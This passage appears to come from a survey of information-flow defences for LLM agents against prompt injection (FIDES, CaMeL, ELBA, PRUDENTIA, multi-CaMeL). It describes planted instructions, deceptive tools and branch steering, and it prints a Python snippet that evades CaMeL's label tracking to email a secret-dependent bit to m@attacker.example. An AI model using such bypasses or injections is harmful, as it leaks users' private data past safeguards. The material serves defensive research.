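Microsoft's FIDES, built by Costa and colleagues, uses the same kinds of label but keeps the ordinary agent loop, in which the model chooses each call after seeing the last reply. If a reply contains untrusted text, FIDES stores the text and shows the model only a name for it. The model can pass the name to another tool, have a reading model answer a question about the text, or open the text itself. Opening the text marks the whole conversation as untrusted, and the policy then refuses calls with important consequences, such as a bank transfer.

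Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with GPT-4o. An ordinary agent let 152 attacks through, after the researchers removed cases that the benchmark had scored wrongly. FIDES let 21 through without policy checks and none with them. Averaged over AgentDojo's four settings, the ordinary agent completed 84% of tasks without policy checks and 42% with them, while FIDES completed 50% with them. FIDES recovered a small part of the drop in completed tasks caused by the checks, and a larger part with o1, a stronger model.

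Some later systems use programming languages that can reject an unsafe program before it runs. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) presents ELBA, in which the agent writes Haskell programs. The types in a Haskell program specify which outside effects it can have, so the developer can require a type that permits only approved operations. TACIT, from *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026), takes a similar approach in another language and completes about as many tasks as CaMeL without splitting the agent in two. *SPA* (2026) extends flow tracking to agents that keep data from one request to the next.

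The table shows how many AgentDojo tasks four systems completed when nobody was attacking them. The models and policies differ, so only CaMeL and ELBA are directly comparable.

| System | Tasks and models | Policy checks off | Policy checks on |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | 21 Slack tasks, four models from 2026 | 13–17 | 4–6 |
| ELBA | The same | 14–18 | 8–10 |
| FIDES | Average of four settings, GPT-4o | 61% | 50% |
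| *SPA* | Average of four settings | 53% | 29% |

About half of SPA's runs stopped because the plan passed untrusted tool output to a tool that accepts only trusted input. Many of those plans were harmless.

Zhou and colleagues also ran a harsher security test, because their models had resisted all 105 Slack attacks without any policy. They changed ELBA so that any subagent that read a planted instruction carried it out. Up to 42% of these attacks succeeded without policies, depending on the model, and none of the 735 attacks on each model succeeded with them. This is better evidence for flow control than the usual attack rates because it tests what happens after a model has been fooled.

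### Why flow tracking needs confined tools

FIDES and its successors protect against hostile data but not against hostile tools. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) state in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* that they trust the tools' code, as earlier systems of this kind did. Costa and colleagues also trust the tools' descriptions. Neither assumption is safe when a stranger wrote the tool server.

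The interpreter controls which values it passes to a tool and how it labels the reply, but it can't follow the data inside the tool. Suppose the lawyer asks a CaMeL agent to convert the contract to PDF. The policy lets the converter receive any document, because converting a document shouldn't require sending it anywhere. The converter makes the PDF and uploads the contract to its developer. Every check passes, because the interpreter doesn't make the upload call. The postmark-mcp package would have passed the checks for the same reason.

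A dishonest tool can also remove labels. The converter could save the contract to a file and, a week later, hide a clause of it in the PDF of a public press release. The interpreter would label that PDF as public, because the press release was the only input it had recorded. The lawyer's agent might then post the PDF on the firm's website. In Costa and colleagues' model, a tool's reply also inherits the labels of any storage the tool reads, but this works only if someone knows which storage it reads.

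Tool descriptions are another problem because the planning model has to read them. A planning model that followed the currency tool's false legal requirement would write the email to the attacker into its program. The attacker's address would then look as trustworthy as the lawyer's own instructions. Kolluri and colleagues' policy lets an agent send data if the decision to send came from a trusted context or if the recipients may read the data. The email would meet the first condition, so the agent would send the contract. A policy that always required the recipients to have permission to read the data would block the email.

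Confining the tools solves the first two problems, because it establishes what each tool can do with the data it receives:

| How the tool starts | What the policy can safely allow |
|---|---|
| Converter with no network and fresh scratch storage | Any document, with the contract's label on the PDF |
| Weather tool that can reach one address | Only data that the forecasting service may read |
| Converter with an open network connection | Only data that its developer may read |

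The last row treats every call to an unconfined tool as a message to a stranger. This is safe, but it means the lawyer can't use that converter for the contract.

Flow tracking protects against the leaks that remain after confinement. A confined currency tool with a clean description can still hide an instruction in its reply, but the planning model never reads the reply, so it can't act on the instruction. Flow tracking also helps with web searches, where a client application has no list of approved recipients to check. If an agent builds a query from the contract, the query inherits the contract's label, and the interpreter can refuse to send it to a search provider that isn't allowed to read the contract. Confining the search tool can't prevent this leak, because the tool needs its connection to the provider.

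Peters-Gill and colleagues make the same point about agents, citing Lampson's 1973 paper. They say guarantees about information flow depend on "agents being suitably confined", and that classical methods for closing covert channels may not be enough for agents that communicate strategically.

### Who writes the policies

Debenedetti and colleagues list having to write and maintain policies as one of CaMeL's main limitations. Willison is wary of any system that asks ordinary users to do this, since he finds Amazon's permission settings hard to understand even after two decades in application security.

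Kolluri and colleagues reply that two general rules cover most tools. A tool with important consequences may run only if untrusted text did not influence the decision to call it. A tool that sends data out may send it only to people allowed to read it. Someone then only has to decide which rule applies to each tool. Confinement helps too, because a client application could automatically apply the lenient policy to any tool it starts without a network connection or shared storage.

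The labels are harder to get right than the rules. Costa and colleagues used an email's sender and recipients to infer who may read it, although the email may have been shared more widely. For their tests, they marked a field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks used it. In real use, nobody knows which fields attackers will use. A cautious user would mark everything from outside as untrusted, and more harmless calls would fail.

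Labels also tend to spread too far. When a model writes a sentence after reading ten files, the interpreter can't determine which of them mattered, so the sentence inherits all ten labels. In a test by *Ghost in the Agent* (2026), FIDES raised false alarms in 94 of 140 cases where untrusted data had not spread, while the paper's own method, NeuroTaint, did so in one. *Sightline* (2026) tries to keep only the labels of inputs that influenced the call, and let none of 34 attack calls through in its test. Such methods could recover some of the lost tasks, but they estimate what influenced the model, so unlike the simple rule of keeping every label, they can drop one that matters.

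### Plans that depend on what the agent reads

CaMeL fixes its plan before it reads any data, so it can't carry out a request such as "do everything on my to-do list", where the steps are in the list. Costa and colleagues classified AgentDojo's tasks and found that the right tool calls depended on data read during the task in about 43% of the banking and Slack tasks, but in 10% or fewer of the others. In total, that is about 20 of the 97 tasks.

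A fixed plan can also go wrong without anyone noticing. In Peters-Gill and colleagues' tests, an agent that couldn't find data for the requested dates sometimes returned data for nearby dates. The program that called it then continued as if the data were right.

FIDES handles some of these tasks with restricted answers. If the user wants a calendar entry for any meeting request in their email, the planning model can check for a request by accepting only a yes or no answer, which can't carry an instruction. ELBA goes further and lets an agent read untrusted text and keep working, but the policy then limits the agent to what the source of that text could do.

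An attacker can still influence a plan by choosing among its existing branches. Suppose the lawyer's program releases the payment details if the notes record that the other side has signed. A false entry in the notes then triggers the payment step, even though the program runs exactly as written. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) calls this branch steering and demonstrates it, for example with fake buttons, on agents that operate a computer through its screen. The paper also tests defences that make more than one check of what the agent sees. The lawyer could require the signed document itself, instead of a line in the notes, before the program releases the payment details.

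### Repeated approval requests

When a policy blocks a call, the agent can ask the user to allow it. Each harmless call the policy blocks then adds another question, and people who see many questions approve nearly all of them, as Claude Code's users did.

Kolluri and colleagues argue that critics should compare agents that use flow tracking with agents such as GitHub Copilot, which already ask before every call that could have consequences. An agent with flow tracking only has to ask about calls that the policy can't clear. In their tests on AgentDojo, even a basic version cut the number of questions by up to a third without completing fewer tasks.

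Their own system, PRUDENTIA, tells the model about the labels and policies so that it can plan around them. It needed up to 1.9 times fewer approvals than FIDES. It can also ask the user to approve a piece of text instead of each action. If an email lists ten tasks, the user can approve the email once, and the agent completes all ten.

This saves nine questions but makes the remaining one much more important. If an attacker has added an eleventh task to the email, a user who skims it approves that task too. PRUDENTIA doesn't offer the same shortcut for releasing private data, because whether a release is appropriate depends too much on the situation. The researchers counted approvals only on harmless tasks and assumed the user would say yes, so their figures don't measure whether people would notice an attack.

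### Leaks through the choice of calls

An agent can reveal private information without sending any private text. If it books a courier only when a contract is signed, the courier company can infer from the booking that the contract was signed. FIDES allows this kind of leak by design. Costa and colleagues say that preventing it would mean banning almost every outwardly visible action once the agent had read anything private.

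CaMeL tries to catch such leaks. If a program sends an email only when the contract price exceeds 100 million, the interpreter treats the email as depending on the price and refuses it. But Garby and colleagues found a way around this, based on an example from the 1970s. Adapted to the contract, it looks like this:

```python
large = True
small = True
if price > 100_000_000:
    small = False
if small:
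    large = False
if large:
    send_email(to="m@attacker.example", body="Large deal")
```

If the price is high, the program sets `small` to false, and the interpreter labels `small` as private. The program then skips the line that would change `large`. CaMeL updates a label only when it runs a line that changes the value, so `large` is still labeled public, and the email goes out. If the price is low, `large` becomes false and no email goes out, so the attacker learns whether the price is high or low by whether the email arrives.

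A planning model that has seen only the user's request would have no reason to write this program. A deceptive tool description might lead the model to write it, which is another reason not to trust tool descriptions.

The leak is one bit, but CaMeL retries programs that fail. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on private data, and CaMeL does not track the retry loop. Garby and colleagues point out that repeated attempts could therefore reveal a whole secret one bit at a time. Peters-Gill and colleagues removed the retries from their version, but it still uses CaMeL's interpreter, which they say needs to track skipped branches properly.

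Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language, LLMbda, to avoid these mistakes, and verified its flow rules with a proof-checking program. With its own checks always on, their agent resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks and completed about as many banking tasks as CaMeL did without policy checks. The proof still allows a run to leak a little information through whether it finishes, and it applies only to what happens inside the language, so it doesn't cover a tool that uploads the contract.

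### Agents that call other agents

A label protects data only as long as the next program enforces it. Peters-Gill and colleagues connected three agents, each running CaMeL. One assigned tasks, one read a database and one sent messages. They asked the agents to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack, and planted an instruction in the database to email the data to an outside address.

The first agent put the summary into its request to the messaging agent. That agent's planning model treated the whole request as coming from its user, so it read the planted instruction and added the email to its program, even though every agent had followed CaMeL's rules.

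The team's extension, multi-CaMeL, splits each request into an instruction and data. The instruction goes to the next agent's planning model. The data travels separately with its labels, and the planning model can't access it. The interpreter blocks any instruction that depends on a tool's reply. With this change, no attack succeeded on any of the five models. Scores on AssetOpsBench fell by another 3.2 percentage points on average, but by less than one point for the two strongest models.

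A third-party tool server may itself be an agent, with a planning model that reads the data sent in each call. Multi-CaMeL protects that data only if the server also keeps instructions separate from data and passes the labels on. A user can't check this on a remote server, so the safest policy is to assume that every call to one sends the data to its operator.
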